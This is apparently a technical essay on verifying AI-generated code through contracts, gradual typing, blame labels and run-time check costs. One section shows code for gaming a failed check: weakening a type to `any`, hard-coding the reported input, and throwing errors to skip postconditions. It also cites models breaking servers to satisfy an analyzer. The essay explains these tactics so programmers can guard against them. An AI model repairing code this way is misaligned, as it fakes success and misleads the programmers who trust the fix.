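Two of the researchers judged the final contracts by hand. Of Qwen3.5-27B's 1,007 contracts, they found 426 correct. Another 276 lacked a requirement, 205 contained an incorrect clause, 51 were vague, 29 had a formal expression that did not match its English description, and the remaining 20 were incomplete. Programs written from correct contracts passed 31% of the time, compared with 6% to 17% for the flawed groups. Task difficulty may explain part of this gap, because harder tasks make both the contract and the program harder to write.

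A mismatch between a contract's expression and its English description is easy to miss. In one contract, the description correctly specified a calculation over every unbroken stretch of a sequence, but the expression performed it only once. Someone who read only the English would have approved the contract, but the program written from it failed.

Qwen3.5-27B was unreliable at reviewing its own contracts. Before repairs, it flagged 296 of the 481 contracts that needed repair and 211 of the 526 that did not. Gidey and colleagues note that using one model to write, review and repair a contract may produce correlated errors.

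Examples with known answers are better at catching an incorrect clause. If the last comparison in guard were reversed, the contract would accept the product that sold 3 as the single best seller and reject the one that sold 9. One example worked out by hand would expose the mistake.

### One author for code and contract

Worked examples matter most when one model writes both the code and the contract. Suppose the model misreads score as a sales rank, where 1 is best, when higher scores are actually better. It sorts from low to high and writes a postcondition that no omitted item may score lower than a returned one. The code satisfies the contract, so every check passes, but the shop gets its worst sellers. Mutation testing would not catch this mistake either, because the mutants would be variations on the wrong program.

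*The Specification as Quality Gate* (2026) argues that two models from the same family do not provide independent checks when they see only the code and have no external specification to compare it with. Two reviewers who each miss 10% of faults would together miss 1% if their errors were independent, but 10% if they missed the same faults.

Asking one model many times doesn't remove the problem. Dai, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Validating Autoformalized Specifications via Contrapuntal Languages*, sampled 30 specifications from Qwen3.6-Flash for a function that should return the last position at which a list's value falls below the one before it, or −1 if there is no such position. Five specifications were correct, but eight shared a mistake that always allowed −1. A vote would have chosen the faulty version, which accepts a program that returns −1 for [6, 0, 1, 2, 3], where the answer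 is 1.

Dai and colleagues instead had the model write each specification in two artificial languages, designed so that a formula in one could not be translated piece by piece into the other. They accepted a specification only if a solver proved the two versions equivalent. Accepted specifications that allowed the correct outputs rejected 98.6% of faulty programs on HumanEval+, compared with 92.8% for the best alternative method. On a harder set of tasks, the figures were 96.2% and 78.3%.

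A simpler precaution is to have a separate session write the checks. *Who Verifies the Builder?* (Sion and April, 2026) reports an experiment in which Claude Sonnet 5.5 wrote three small services and its own tests for them. A new session of the same model, without the builder's conversation, wrote tests from the specification and then added more after reading the code. The builder's tests caught 85.1% of 46 planted faults on average, and the new session's caught 95.4%. When GPT-5.5, a model from another company, replaced the new session, its tests caught 85.1%, no better than the builder's. With only one pair of models, the experiment could not separate the effect of independence from that of ability.

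Sion and April never observed a shared misunderstanding, because the builder's programs were all correct, but the builder had left some behaviour untested. For example, the key that prevents duplicate payments was correctly tied to a user in the builder's code, but its tests still passed when a planted fault tied the key to a login session instead. The new session also raised questions about gaps in the specification, some of which the researchers had left deliberately.

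A check's quality may depend more on what its writer knows than on who wrote it. In *Specification Grounding Drives Test Effectiveness for LLM Code*, Haeri and Ghelichi (2026) had Claude Sonnet 4.6 test 30 faulty drafts of small functions. It caught 18 when given the short request and told to cover edge cases, all 30 when given a written list of the function's rules, and 27 when given the same rules in a paragraph. When the rules about invalid input were removed, it caught only 6. The researchers had chosen requests that omitted important edge cases, so the rules gave the tester information that the code's author lacked.

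That advantage is the reason for writing the rules down. *TestSuiteBench* (2026) likewise reports that more detailed specifications raised the mutation scores of test suites written by coding agents from 4.0% to 25.5%. But mistakes in the rules also carry over into the tests. When Haeri and Ghelichi added rules that defined the bugs as correct behaviour, the tests still caught all 30 faulty drafts, but 15 of the 87 tests now required the wrong behaviour.

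### Who should write the contract?

Models can draft contracts easily, and even imperfect drafts can help. Chen and colleagues had Qwen3-8B write ten programs per puzzle and used the model's own contracts to choose among them. The share of puzzles solved by the chosen program rose from 59.4% to 62.2%. A draft can also reveal a mistake in the documentation. One contract examined by Richter and Wehrheim followed the description and required the error of an approximate square root to be less than a given tolerance, but the reference solution also allowed an error equal to the tolerance. For 2 and a tolerance of 0.25, the solution returned 1.5, whose square is off by exactly 0.25. The developers then had to decide whether to correct the code or the description.

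The case against model-written contracts is that models have been much better at writing code than contracts. Chen and colleagues compared the two on issues from real codebases. Claude 4.5 Sonnet solved 77.2% of the issues but wrote adequate contracts for only about a fifth. Newer models probably do better at both but may still be worse at contracts, so a programmer who trusts a model's contracts because its code is usually good may overrate them.

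For pickTop, the shop's programmer should at least write the rules and a few examples, including bad input, before seeing any generated code. A model in a fresh session can then turn these into a contract, which the programmer can read and run on the examples and some mutants.

Reading a contract is not enough to tell whether it leaves something out. Silva and colleagues checked 218 Dafny specifications that people had labelled strong or weak by hand, and proved that 19 of those labelled strong were weak. Mutants make such gaps easier to see. A programmer reading `guard` could easily miss that it lacks a clause about repeats, but would be unlikely to miss the same product appearing twice in a list of two best sellers.

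## Choose how much of a type to check at run time

The type signature of pickTop already contains part of its contract. A compiler can generate run-time checks for that part, so nobody has to write them by hand as in guard. TypeScript checks none of the type at run time, some languages check all of it, and others check only its outermost layer.

### The dynamic type and casts

Siek and Taha (2006), in *Gradual Typing for Functional Languages*, let the dynamic type ? stand for all or part of a type. The type Product → ? describes a function that takes a product and returns a value of unknown type. Their checker rejects a program only when the known parts of two types conflict.

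They define the absence of conflict as a relation called consistency, with the symbol ~. Four rules cover the basic language:

```text
T ~ T
T ~ ?
? ~ T
A → R  ~  B → S     if A ~ B and R ~ S
```

If pickTop requires a callback of type Product → number, the checker accepts one of type Product → ?, because its result may turn out to be a number. It rejects one of type Product → string.

Consistency is symmetric but not transitive. For example, string is consistent with ?, and ? is consistent with number, but string is not consistent with number. If consistency were transitive, every type would be consistent with every other through ?, and the checker could never reject anything.

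An earlier design by Satish Thatte treated the dynamic type as a supertype of all the others and let the checker convert a value up to it and then down to another type. Two such conversions let the checker treat a boolean as a number, so the system could accept a call that passed true to a function on numbers. Thatte added a second pass to look for impossible conversions, but Siek and Taha showed that the system could still accept this call.

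Their own checker rejects the call, but it lets a similar mistake through if the program takes two steps:

```ts
const n: any = "three";
pickTop(products, n, score);
```

In TypeScript, the dynamic type is called any. Each line is acceptable by itself, because a string may be assigned to n and n may be passed as k. The compiler described by Siek and Taha would insert a cast, which tests at run time whether a value fits a given type. The second line would become pickTop(products, ⟨number⟩ n, score), and the cast would fail on "three" and stop the program with an error. TypeScript inserts no cast, so pickTop runs with "three" as k.

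For each call, the compiler compares the argument's type with the parameter's type and casts the argument only if the types differ but are consistent. If the function has type ?, the compiler casts the function. A cast to a function type produces a wrapper, so ⟨Product → number⟩ score becomes p => ⟨number⟩ score(p). A fully annotated program gets no casts. Siek and Taha used the proof assistant Isabelle to prove that their checker accepts exactly the fully annotated programs that an ordinary static checker would.

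In the same year, Sam Tobin-Hochstadt and Matthias Felleisen published a design for moving an existing untyped program to types module by module. It grew into Typed Racket, which has no dynamic type. A typed module that imports something from an untyped one must declare a type for it, and the compiler inserts the checks at that import. This suits generated code, which often arrives as a whole function or file with a clear boundary.

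### Adding and removing annotations

A programmer who adds types to a working program a few at a time needs to know how each annotation might affect it. In *Refined Criteria for Gradual Typing*, Siek, Vitousek and colleagues (2015) addressed this by proposing the gradual guarantee. It requires that a program that passes the type checker still passes after someone removes annotations, and that if it produced a value before, it still produces an equivalent one.

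Adding annotations is riskier, because an annotation can be wrong. The checker may then reject the program, or a cast may stop it. But if the program still finishes, the guarantee requires it to give the same answer as before.

Some published designs fail this test, including TS*, a variant of JavaScript intended to protect against security holes. For example, a program might pass the callback x => x to a function that calls it with true. TS* runs this program correctly when nothing is annotated and when everything is. If only the function that receives the callback is annotated, TS* stops the program, because it does not allow a function of type ? → ? to be used as one of type boolean → boolean. A shop that annotated pickTop before score could break a working program in the same way, and would have to annotate score as well to get it running again.

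Typed Racket fails for another reason. To enforce a type variable such as the T in pickTop's signature, it seals each value in an opaque package, just as the stricter contract hid each product from pickTop. Siek and colleagues describe a function that tests whether its argument is an integer. Given 5, it returns true when the function has the dynamic type and false when it has a type with a type variable, because the sealed 5 is no longer an integer. If a generated pickTop treated numbers differently from other items, adding the correct signature could change its result without any error.

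Even a language with no run-time checks can satisfy the gradual guarantee, as Greenman, Dimoulas and Felleisen (2023) point out in *Typed–Untyped Interactions*. Removing an annotation cannot change how a program runs if the annotation had no effect at run time.

### One fault under three strategies

To compare ways of enforcing types, Greenman and colleagues take one small language and run its programs under several sets of rules. The static checker stays the same throughout. Three of these strategies exist in full programming languages:

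- Deep types cover the whole of a type. At the boundary, the language inspects plain data down to the last element and puts functions in wrappers.
- Shallow types cover only a value's outermost shape, such as "a list" or "a function". They use no wrappers. Instead, typed code repeats these small checks at the boundary, at the start of each typed function, and whenever it calls a function or takes an element out of a data structure.
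- Erased types have no effect at run time.

The same comparison works for pickTop. In the program below, the shop's module is typed and the generated module is not. The generated module has one of the faults from the mutation test and returns sales figures instead of products. A Product has a string for its name and a number for its sales. The signature uses Product instead of T to keep sealing out of the example.

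```text
 1  // generated.js, untyped
 2  export const pickTop = (items, k, score) =>
 3    items.map(item => score(item)).toSorted((a, b) => b - a).slice(0, k);
 4
 5  // shop.ts, typed
 6  type PickTop = (items: Product[], k: number,
 7                  score: (p: Product) => number) => Product[];
 8  const pickTop: PickTop = generated.pickTop;
 9  const best = pickTop(products, 2, p => p.sales);
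10  const first = best[0];
11  const label = "Best seller: " + first.name;
```

With sales of 3, 9 and 5, the generated function returns the list [9, 5]. The static checker reports no errors in the shop's module because it treats the declaration on lines 6 to 8 as correct. TypeScript would run this program with erased types. The other two columns of the table show what would happen if the TypeScript compiler followed the rules for shallow or deep types.

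| Line | Erased | Shallow | Deep |
|---|---|---|---|
| 8 | no check | pickTop is a function: passes | pickTop is a function: passes and gets a wrapper |
| 9 | no check | the result is a list: passes | every member is a Product: fails on 9 |
| 10 | no check | the member is an object: fails on 9 | not reached |
| 11 | label is "Best seller: undefined" | not reached | not reached |

Under erased types the program never reports an error. The number 9 has no name, so JavaScript supplies undefined, and the shop advertises it.

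The deep column is for lists that cannot change once built, as in Racket. JavaScript arrays can change, so a deep language would put this one in a wrapper and check members as code reads them, which would move the failure to line 10. The wrapper would still stay on the array when another module receives it, so reads there would be checked too.

Shallow types can catch a different fault, in which the generated code calls score with positions instead of products, as in an earlier example. The callback on line 9 is typed code, so it checks its own argument, and score(0) fails immediately because 0 is not an object. If the callback had come from an untyped module, nothing would check the argument.

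When types are erased, typed code can contradict its own annotations. Greenman and colleagues show this with Flow, a type checker for JavaScript. In their example, a function annotated to take and return a number adds 1 to its argument. When untyped code passes the function to itself, JavaScript converts the function to text and appends a 1, so the function returns a string instead of a number.

### Which languages use which strategy

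Erased types are by far the most common. In their 2023 survey, Greenman and colleagues placed TypeScript, Flow, Hack and the Python checkers mypy, Pyre and Pytype in this group. Erased types appeal to programmers because programs run as they would without types, at the same speed, and programmers still get error reports and better code completion in their editors.

Deep types came mostly from academic groups, and the survey lists Typed Racket, Gradualtalk and Grift as examples. Shallow types began with Reticulated Python, a research version of Python. The survey also lists Pallene, a typed companion to Lua, and Grace as languages with shallow types.

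C#, Dart 2 and the research language Nom use another strategy, concrete types, in which each value carries a tag that identifies its full type. A program can tell whether a value fits a type by checking only the tag, but it must attach the right tag when it creates the value. A Nom programmer cannot create a plain pair and later treat it as a pair of integers, but must declare a separate kind of pair for each combination of types. Generated code in Nom would have to use the shop's own declarations from the start, so nobody could add an untyped function as on line 8.

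Several languages mix strategies. Pyret, a teaching language, fully checks data of fixed size, such as pairs, but checks only the outermost shape of lists and functions, so it would let [9, 5] through at the boundary. Sorbet, which adds types to Ruby, can optionally check method signatures at run time.

### Faults that pass between untyped modules

Under shallow types, line 10 caught the fault because typed code took a member out of the list. Many typed modules never do that. Suppose the shop deletes lines 10 and 11 and exports best, and an untyped module, page.js, displays the list:

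```js
// page.js, untyped
show("Best seller: " + best[0].name);
```

With deep types, the program still stops at line 9. With shallow types, it now runs to the end and displays "Best seller: undefined", as it does with erased types. The list started and ended in untyped code, and the typed module in between checked only that it was a list before passing it on.

The shallow language is still type sound. In a sound language, if an expression produces a value, the value fits a prediction based on the expression's type, and typed code never applies an operation to a value that cannot support it. For shallow types, the prediction covers only the value's outermost shape, so [9, 5] fits because it is a list. For untyped code, the prediction is only that the result is a valid value of some kind, so 9 fits too.

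Shallow types can also miss a wrong argument to a function. *Deep and Shallow Types for Gradual Languages* (Greenman, 2022) gives an example in which an untyped library supplies a function that draws text. A typed module re-exports the function with a correct signature, from a string and a font object to a picture. An untyped client then calls it with the strings "cat" and "roman". Deep types reject "roman". Shallow types check only that the library supplied a function, after which the client calls the library directly, without its arguments being checked against the signature.

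Greenman and colleagues found the same pattern in more realistic code, built around a popular Python library for web requests. A typed module in Reticulated Python declared that a timeout is a pair of numbers. The client passed a pair whose second member was the string "zero". Reticulated confirmed that the value was a pair and accepted it, and the library raised an error several calls deeper, just as it would have without any types. The typed module still appeared in the error's list of active calls, which gave the programmer a clue to the source. If the library had stored the pair and read it later, the module would not have been in that list.

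The mistake may also be in the declaration. A typed interface to one of Racket's networking libraries declared that a callback would receive a string, but the library passed it a structured URL. Both the library and the client were untyped. The client's author had trusted the declaration and written a callback for strings. Typed Racket, with deep types, stopped the program when the library called the callback. A programmer who asks a model to write type declarations for an untyped library can expect similar errors, and under shallow or erased types a wrong declaration could go unnoticed.

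### Soundness, complete monitoring and vigilance

Greenman and colleagues describe a strategy, Forgetful, that lets such values through even though it satisfies the full version of soundness, as deep types do, and not just the weaker shallow version. Forgetful wraps functions and data when they enter typed code and discards the wrappers when they leave. In one example, a function that returns its argument unchanged passes through typed code as a function on natural numbers, then goes back to untyped code, which applies it to the pair (2, 8). Deep types stop the program, whereas Forgetful returns the pair and remains sound because no typed code received it.

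Greenman and colleagues therefore add complete monitoring, a property first developed for contracts. In a gradually typed language, it is meant to ensure that every value crossing between typed and untyped code is checked against its whole type, even long after the first call. To test for this property, they label each value with the modules responsible for it. A full check replaces the old labels with the receiving module's label, and a wrapper keeps the two sides' labels separate. If a value carries the labels of two modules with no wrapper between them, it has crossed without a full check. Under shallow types, the list [9, 5] reaches that state as soon as it enters the shop's module.

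Deep types satisfy complete monitoring, unlike shallow, erased and Forgetful types. In the formal model, any program that stops with an error under erased types also stops under shallow types, and any that stops under shallow types also stops under deep types.

*Gradually Typed Languages Should Be Vigilant!* (Gierczak, Menon and colleagues, 2024) argues that neither soundness nor complete monitoring is enough. Soundness considers only the type that the current code expects and ignores the types a value had on the way there. The formal definition of complete monitoring fixes where checks must happen but not what they test, so a language whose checks all did nothing could still satisfy it. Shallow types fail complete monitoring, but the property doesn't identify what a programmer can rely on when using them.

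Their alternative, vigilance, depends on a record of every type that a value has passed through. A language is vigilant for a type system if each value fits all the types in its record. In page.js, the record of [9, 5] contains ?, then Product[], then ? again. Soundness requires the list to fit only the last entry, which any value fits, but vigilance also requires it to fit Product[], which it does not.

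| | Deep | Shallow | Erased |
|---|---|---|---|
| What soundness predicts in typed code | the full type | the outermost shape | some valid value |
| Complete monitoring | yes | no | no |
| Vigilant for full types | yes | no | not studied |
| Vigilant for outermost shapes | no | yes | not studied |
| Works without wrappers | no | yes | yes |

Deep types get a "no" in the fourth row because of where their checks are, even though checking a whole type would seem to include checking its shape. The compiler puts a deep function's argument checks at the places where less precisely typed code calls it, not inside the function, and it needs the function's full type to do so. If the type system records only that the value is a function, those checks disappear. A shallow function tests its own arguments, so it keeps its shape check whoever calls it.

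Gierczak and colleagues also found that shallow checks can together establish more than a value's outermost shape. In one of their examples, a typed function splits a picture into foreground and background, then crops both parts with another typed function. The typed cropping code checks each part, so the result must be a pair of pictures, although shallow types alone guarantee only a pair. With a stronger type system that tracks such facts, they also proved that a compiler can leave out some of the checks.

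The shop can exploit this effect before it exports the list to page.js:

```ts
export const checked = best.map((p: Product) => p);
```

The callback is a typed function, so under shallow types it checks that each member is an object and fails on 9. Checking the name and sales inside each product would require typed code to read those fields too. Under erased types, the callback checks nothing, so the line is useless.

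People seem to expect types to behave as deep types do. Greenman cites a survey about a hypothetical gradual language, where participants called the results that shallow types allow "unexpected" more often than those that deep types allow.

### Deep and shallow types in one program

Deep types can slow a program badly when values cross a boundary often, which is the main reason to use anything weaker. Greenman's design lets a programmer make each module deep, shallow or untyped. Deep and shallow modules use the same type checker, and in Greenman's version of Typed Racket, switching a module between them usually means changing one line.

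The compiler chooses the check for each boundary from the kinds of module on either side:

| Value passes | Check |
|---|---|
| between a deep module and a shallow or untyped one, in either direction | the whole type, with a wrapper if needed |
| from an untyped module to a shallow one | the outermost shape |
| from a shallow module to an untyped one | none |
| between two deep or two shallow modules | none |

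A deep module cannot rely on the types of values from a shallow module, even though both modules passed the same type checker. Such a value may have started in untyped code and had only its outer shape checked, as [9, 5] did. A full check at every boundary of a deep module keeps out values that don't match their types. Greenman proved that, in a mixed program, deep modules retain complete monitoring and shallow modules retain their weaker soundness. In the example, the shop could make the module that imports generated.js deep and leave the rest of its typed code shallow.

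Deep types also stop some programs that would otherwise work. Programmers often use Typed Racket's most general type, Any, as a placeholder when they don't want to commit to a more specific one. With deep types, untyped code that receives a value of type Any can't call it if it is a function, or write to it if it is a mutable container. Shallow types allow both. Greenman also counted 12 rarely used types for which Typed Racket had no deep wrapper. A failed deep check in generated code may therefore mean that the annotation was stricter than anyone intended.

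Greenman suggests starting with deep types, because their checks help find logical errors. If the program becomes too slow, the programmer can switch to shallow types, then return to deep types once all the critical boundaries have types on both sides. This advice is based on experience rather than a controlled test.

### A rule for generated code

The right strategy depends on which side of the boundary has the types and on where the values go afterwards.

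When typed code uses untyped generated code, deep types should be the default. They are most valuable if the typed module passes results on to untyped code, as the shop does with page.js, or if the generated code returns a function that another module will call later. Shallow types are enough if typed code itself reads every part of the result that the program uses. A programmer can judge whether it does by following the result from the call to its last use.

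In the reverse arrangement, the model writes a typed pickTop and the shop is untyped. The static checker examines the generated body before it runs, and would reject the version that returns sales figures because a list of numbers is not a list of products. This alone is a good reason to ask a model for annotated code. The run-time checks then mostly protect pickTop from the shop's mistakes, and shallow types do this well. They catch "three" when it arrives as k, and a score of "9" when the typed body receives it from the callback. But if pickTop passes score to an untyped sorting library, the library would call score directly, and only a deep type's wrapper would check the results.

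If both sides of a call have types, the static checker covers the call, and two deep modules need no run-time check there. A model can defeat this by annotating a value as `any`, because the checker then accepts the value wherever it is used. A language with run-time casts still checks the value where the code expects a known type. TypeScript does not, so a programmer reviewing generated TypeScript should search for `any` and for type assertions, which override the checker in a similar way.

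Most programmers can't choose a strategy, because they already work in TypeScript or in Python with a checker like mypy, where types are erased. They have to rely on a contract at the boundary for run-time checks. The guard function rejects [9, 5] when pickTop returns, since 9 is not one of the products. It also checks properties that deep types don't, such as the range of k. The module that imports generated.js should apply guard and export only the checked function, so that page.js gets the same protection as the typed code.

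## Use a failed check to find and repair the fault

Under deep types, the program that received sales figures instead of products stops on the number 9. In the format Typed Racket uses, the error would look roughly like this:

```text
pickTop: broke its own contract
  promised: Product
  produced: 9
  in: an element of the result of
      (items, k, score) => Product[]
  blaming: generated.js
  (assuming the contract is correct)
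```

The message gives the broken condition, the value that broke it and a blame label, which here is generated.js. The label means only that a value from that module crossed the boundary and did not fit the declared type. It does not show where in the module the fault lies, and the fault may be outside the module, for example if pickTop got its list from a faulty sorting library. The declared type may also be wrong, which is why the message ends with a caveat.

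### Why blame falls on the less typed side

Wadler and Findler (2009), in *Well-typed programs can't be blamed*, worked out which side of a cast can be blamed. Every cast in their system carries a label, which receives positive blame if the value inside the cast did not fit the type and negative blame if the code around the cast misused the value. These correspond to the supplier p and the user n in the wrapping rule for contracts.

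By their theorem, the side of a cast with the more precise type is never blamed. A cast from a less precise type to a more precise one never produces negative blame, and a cast from a more precise type to a less precise one never produces positive blame. The type number → number is more precise than ? → ?, and a type with an added condition, such as "integers of at least 0", is more precise than the plain type of integers.

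For plain values the reason is simple. A cast from ? to number can fail, and then the value is at fault. A cast from number to ? cannot fail, because everything fits ?. A cast on a function splits into a cast on its result and a cast on its argument. The argument travels the other way, so its cast runs in the opposite direction with the label swapped:

```text
function cast from ? → ? to number → number
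    result:    ? to number     may fail: positive blame
    argument:  number to ?     cannot fail

function cast from number → number to ? → ?
    result:    number to ?     cannot fail
    argument:  ? to number     may fail: negative blame
```

Only the untyped side can get the blame, which is the function in the first case and the caller in the second. With a callback inside a callback, the direction and the label flip together again, so the blame stays with the less precise side.

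Suppose the untyped pickTop calls the shop's typed score with the position 0. If the shop casts pickTop to its declared type on import, the misuse comes from inside the cast and the blame is positive. If the shop casts score to ? and passes it to pickTop, the misuse comes from outside the cast and the blame is negative. In both cases, the blame falls on the generated code.

The full proof divides ordinary subtyping, which describes casts that cannot fail, into two relations, one that rules out positive blame and one that rules out negative blame. Precision in the theorem means that the first relation holds between two types in one direction and the second holds in the reverse direction.

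One type has to be more precise than the other in every part. A cast from number → ? to ? → number makes the result more precise and the argument less precise, so either side may get the blame.

### A wrong type can put the blame on correct code

The theorem compares the precision of two types without establishing that either is correct. The typed module may contain a wrong type or any fault that breaks no type, such as a reversed sort.

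A faulty declaration can lead the checker to blame correct code. This happened with the declaration for Racket's networking library described earlier. According to *Complete Monitors for Gradual Types* (Greenman, Felleisen and Dimoulas, 2019), Typed Racket reported that the library had broken the contract. The library had been part of Racket for two decades and was behaving as intended, but Typed Racket treated the declaration as correct.

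The same thing could happen to pickTop. If the shop's programmer mistakenly declares that score takes a product's name, a correct pickTop that passes whole products will get the blame. A model given this message and told to repair pickTop may break working code. Before acting on a label, the programmer should compare the failed clause with the original request.

### Sound and complete blame

Blame can also be wrong because the language has not kept a full record of where a value came from. Greenman and colleagues defined two properties to measure this, using labels that record which modules are responsible for a value. Blame is sound if it lists only responsible modules, even if it misses some of them. It is complete if it lists every responsible module, even if it also includes others.

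| | Deep | Shallow | Erased |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blame soundness | yes | no | yes |
| Blame completeness | yes | no | no |

Erased types satisfy blame soundness only because they never assign blame. Deep types satisfy both blame soundness and blame completeness because each wrapper stores the names of the two parties at its boundary.

Shallow types have no wrappers to record which boundaries a value has crossed. Reticulated Python instead keeps this information in a global map and reports the offending value's entries when a check fails. The reported list can include irrelevant modules and omit responsible ones. The map works especially poorly for built-in functions that take callbacks. In a call such as filter(f, xs), the values that f receives come from the list xs, but the map does not record that connection.

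A language can assign blame precisely without checking every value against its whole type. In their later comparison, Greenman and colleagues include a strategy called Amnesic, which makes the same checks as shallow types but uses wrappers to record the boundaries a value has crossed. Amnesic lacks complete monitoring, but its blame is sound and complete. It exists only as a theoretical model.

### A simulated programmer who follows the blame

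These properties do not establish that blame saves anyone work. *How to Evaluate Blame for Gradual Types* (Lazarek, Greenman and colleagues, 2021) tests whether it does, using an algorithm called the rational programmer. The algorithm reads an error, adds types to the untyped module that the error points to, and runs the type checker. If the checker rejects the module, the algorithm has found the fault. Otherwise, it runs the program again and follows the next error. It fails when an error points to no untyped module.

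In one small example, an untyped server module has a function that should return a number no greater than zero but just flips the sign of its argument. An untyped middle module multiplies the result by 4, and a typed main module calls the middle one with −10. The first error reports the value 40 and blames the middle module. Once the middle module has types, the error reports 10 and blames the server. When the server gets types too, the type checker rejects it.

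In the experiment, Lazarek and colleagues planted faults, such as swapped arguments, in ten Typed Racket programs with 6 to 14 modules each. They kept only faults that the type checker would catch in a fully typed program and that caused a run-time error in a fully untyped one. The stack trace, which lists the calls in progress when an error occurs, had to include at least three modules so that the search was not trivial. They sampled 752 faulty programs and tried each with 96 random choices of which modules had types, for a total of 72,192 scenarios.

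They also ran the deep and shallow versions with the blame label ignored, to separate the value of blame from the value of the checks. In those runs the algorithm followed the stack trace, as it always had to under erased types.

Blame led to the fault in 85–90% of scenarios with either deep or shallow types, while stack traces led to it in less than 80%, however the language enforced types. Deep types with blame succeeded in about 11% of scenarios where the same checks without blame failed, and the reverse never happened. The advantage over erased types was almost 12%. When both methods worked, blame rarely shortened the search, and in most cases the algorithm had to add types to only one module.

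One of the extra successes involved a card game in which the player module offered a method under a different name from the one the dealer module expected. Deep types blamed player, and adding types there exposed the mistake. The stack trace from the same failed check listed only the main module, which already had types, so the search that ignored blame got stuck at once.

The selection of faults favoured erased types, because every fault had to cause an error even without type checks. In a preliminary run on three programs, Lazarek and colleagues included all faults that deep types could detect, and the results suggested a much larger advantage for deep types with blame. Shallow blame looks better in these figures than it would in practice, because keeping its map slowed programs by a factor of 133 on average.

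### When the declaration is wrong

The 2021 experiment assumed that all the types were correct, which is generous for TypeScript. TypeScript programmers rely on a public repository of type declarations for thousands of JavaScript libraries. People other than the libraries' authors often write these declarations, and misspelled field names are among their most common mistakes.

In *How to Evaluate Blame for Gradual Types, Part 2*, Lazarek, Greenman and colleagues (2023) therefore planted faults in the declarations. They divided the same ten programs into a client, a library and a typed interface between them, then changed the interface, for example by swapping the types of two arguments. An adaptor made the client behave as if it had been written for the wrong type. They kept 294 faulty interfaces and ran 100 scenarios with each.

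| What the search followed | Faults in code | Faults in declarations |
|---|---|---|
| Deep types, blame | 85–90% | nearly 90% |
| Shallow types, blame | 85–90% | nearly 70% |
| Deep types, stack trace | under 80% | about 45% |
| Shallow types, stack trace | under 80% | slightly below erased |
| Erased types, stack trace | under 80% | just under 65% |

Deep types gave the best result with blame and the worst without it. They catch a bad value as it crosses the interface, when the stack trace usually contains only client modules, although the conflict is between the interface and the library. Under erased types, the program runs until an operation fails, and by then the library is more often in the trace. Without a blame label, an early check can therefore produce a trace that omits the module the programmer needs to read.

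Lazarek and colleagues recommend erasing types in deployed programs, where speed matters, and switching to deep types with blame to reproduce and debug a fault. This works only if faults cause visible errors without the checks. In their data, erased types let the program finish without an error in about 1,200 of the 29,400 scenarios, or 4%. But Racket stops at many errors that JavaScript ignores, such as the one that made the shop advertise "undefined". So for generated JavaScript, leaving a contract such as guard switched on is safer, at least until the slowdown becomes a problem.

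Both experiments simulate the programmer with an algorithm that doesn't act on hunches and always has a correctly typed version of each module to swap in. The algorithm counts modules rather than hours, so the percentages measure how often the information is good enough to lead to the fault, not how much time a person would save.

The algorithm's main step is easy to copy for pickTop. If the label is generated.js, the programmer can ask a model to annotate that file without the type any, and then run the type checker, which would reject the version that returns sales figures. If the type checker accepts the annotated file and the run-time check still fails, the next places to look are any untyped libraries that pickTop uses and the contract itself.

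### Giving the message to a model

A model can take the programmer's place in this loop, but the two experiments do not measure how well. The rational programmer is a fixed rule, not a language model. In the Rust experiment by Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, a model repaired most of its compilation failures using the compiler's error messages, but those messages had no blame labels. A compiler can also locate such faults in the text, whereas a failed contract gives a value, and the model must work out which line produced it.

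The label's most obvious use is to decide which code a repair system sends to the model. When the shop's score function returns the string "9", a system that follows the label would send score and leave pickTop alone.

The message should also contain the failing call. As written, guard reports only a party and a reason, such as "an omitted item scores higher". It would be more useful if it added that the sales were 3, 9 and 5, that k was 1, and that the function returned the product that sold 3. A model or a person can guess from these values that the sort is reversed. Tests by Lim and colleagues give indirect support for including such values. Small models that already had the input rules rejected more bad inputs after they also saw examples. Those models were writing new programs, however, so the result may not carry over to repair.

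### Repairs that only satisfy the check

A model told to make an error disappear can do so without fixing the fault. The simplest way is to weaken the check. In the shop's typed module, one edit is enough:

```text
type PickTop = (items: Product[], k: number,
                score: (p: Product) => number) => any;
```

This edit changes the result type from `Product[]` to `any`. A cast to the dynamic type cannot fail, so even deep types let the list `[9, 5]` through, and the shop advertises "undefined" again. Deleting the last clause of `guard` has a similar effect on the reversed sort. Such an edit can look like a successful repair because the program now runs to the end and the rest of the code is unchanged.

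The models in the study by Lunghi and colleagues showed a similar tendency when they broke web servers to satisfy an analyzer whose check was wrong for the task. When the contract is correct and the code is faulty, the model may instead change the contract. Telling it not to may not be enough, so the type declarations and guard belong in files that the model cannot edit.

The model can also leave the check alone and handle only the input in the message:

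```js
if (items.length === 3 && k === 1) return [items[1]];
return [...items].sort((a, b) => score(a) - score(b)).slice(0, k);
```

This returns the right product for sales of 3, 9 and 5, and keeps the reversed sort for everything else. It would pass a test suite that contains only the reported call. A contract is harder to satisfy this way, because guard applies the same condition to every call and would reject the answer as soon as the best seller of three was not in the middle. To find the fault before customers do, the programmer should run the repaired function on inputs the model has not seen, with different lengths, orders and values of k.

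A third way for generated code to avoid the postcondition is to throw its own error on difficult inputs, because the postcondition runs only when the code returns. To prevent this, the guard function can catch any error that neither it nor score raised and blame the generated code.

A locked contract may itself contain the mistake. If the precondition is wrong, such as k > 0 instead of k ≥ 0, no change to pickTop can fix it. The model therefore needs a way to flag a clause as possibly wrong, along with the call that shows the problem, and a person should decide whether to change the clause. After any change, the programmer can rerun the contract on the wrong versions of pickTop from the mutation test. If the new contract accepts a version that the old one rejected, the change has weakened it.

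## Measure and reduce the cost of run-time checks

Run-time checks slow some programs by a few percent and others by a factor of 100. Most of the difference comes from how often values cross the boundary, which the programmer doesn't control when a model writes the code on the other side. Two correct versions of pickTop can return the same products on every call, yet one can trigger twenty times as many checks as the other.

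### Counting the checks on pickTop

Greenman, Takikawa and colleagues (2019), in *How to evaluate the performance of gradual type systems*, trace the slowdown in Typed Racket to the time spent checking values as they cross between typed and untyped code, creating wrappers for them, and going through those wrappers at each later use. Wrappers can also pile up on a function that crosses repeatedly.

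Checking a list requires checking each element. If the shop's untyped code passes an unchangeable list of 1,000 products to the typed function pickTop, deep types require three tests per product: that it is an object, that its name is a string and that its sales figure is a number. Those 3,000 tests take little time if the list crosses into typed code only once. But in one example from Greenman and colleagues, untyped code calls a typed function a million times to test whether a stack is empty, and Typed Racket checks the stack against its list type every time.

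*Exploiting Multiple Abstract Call Patterns for Optimizing Run-Time Checks* (Ferreiro, Jurjo-Rivas and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar problem in recursive code. A search steps through a list, and its contract checks at each step that the remainder is still a list. The search alone takes time proportional to the list's length, but the checks take time proportional to the square of the length. For 1,000 items, the checks would examine 500,500 elements.

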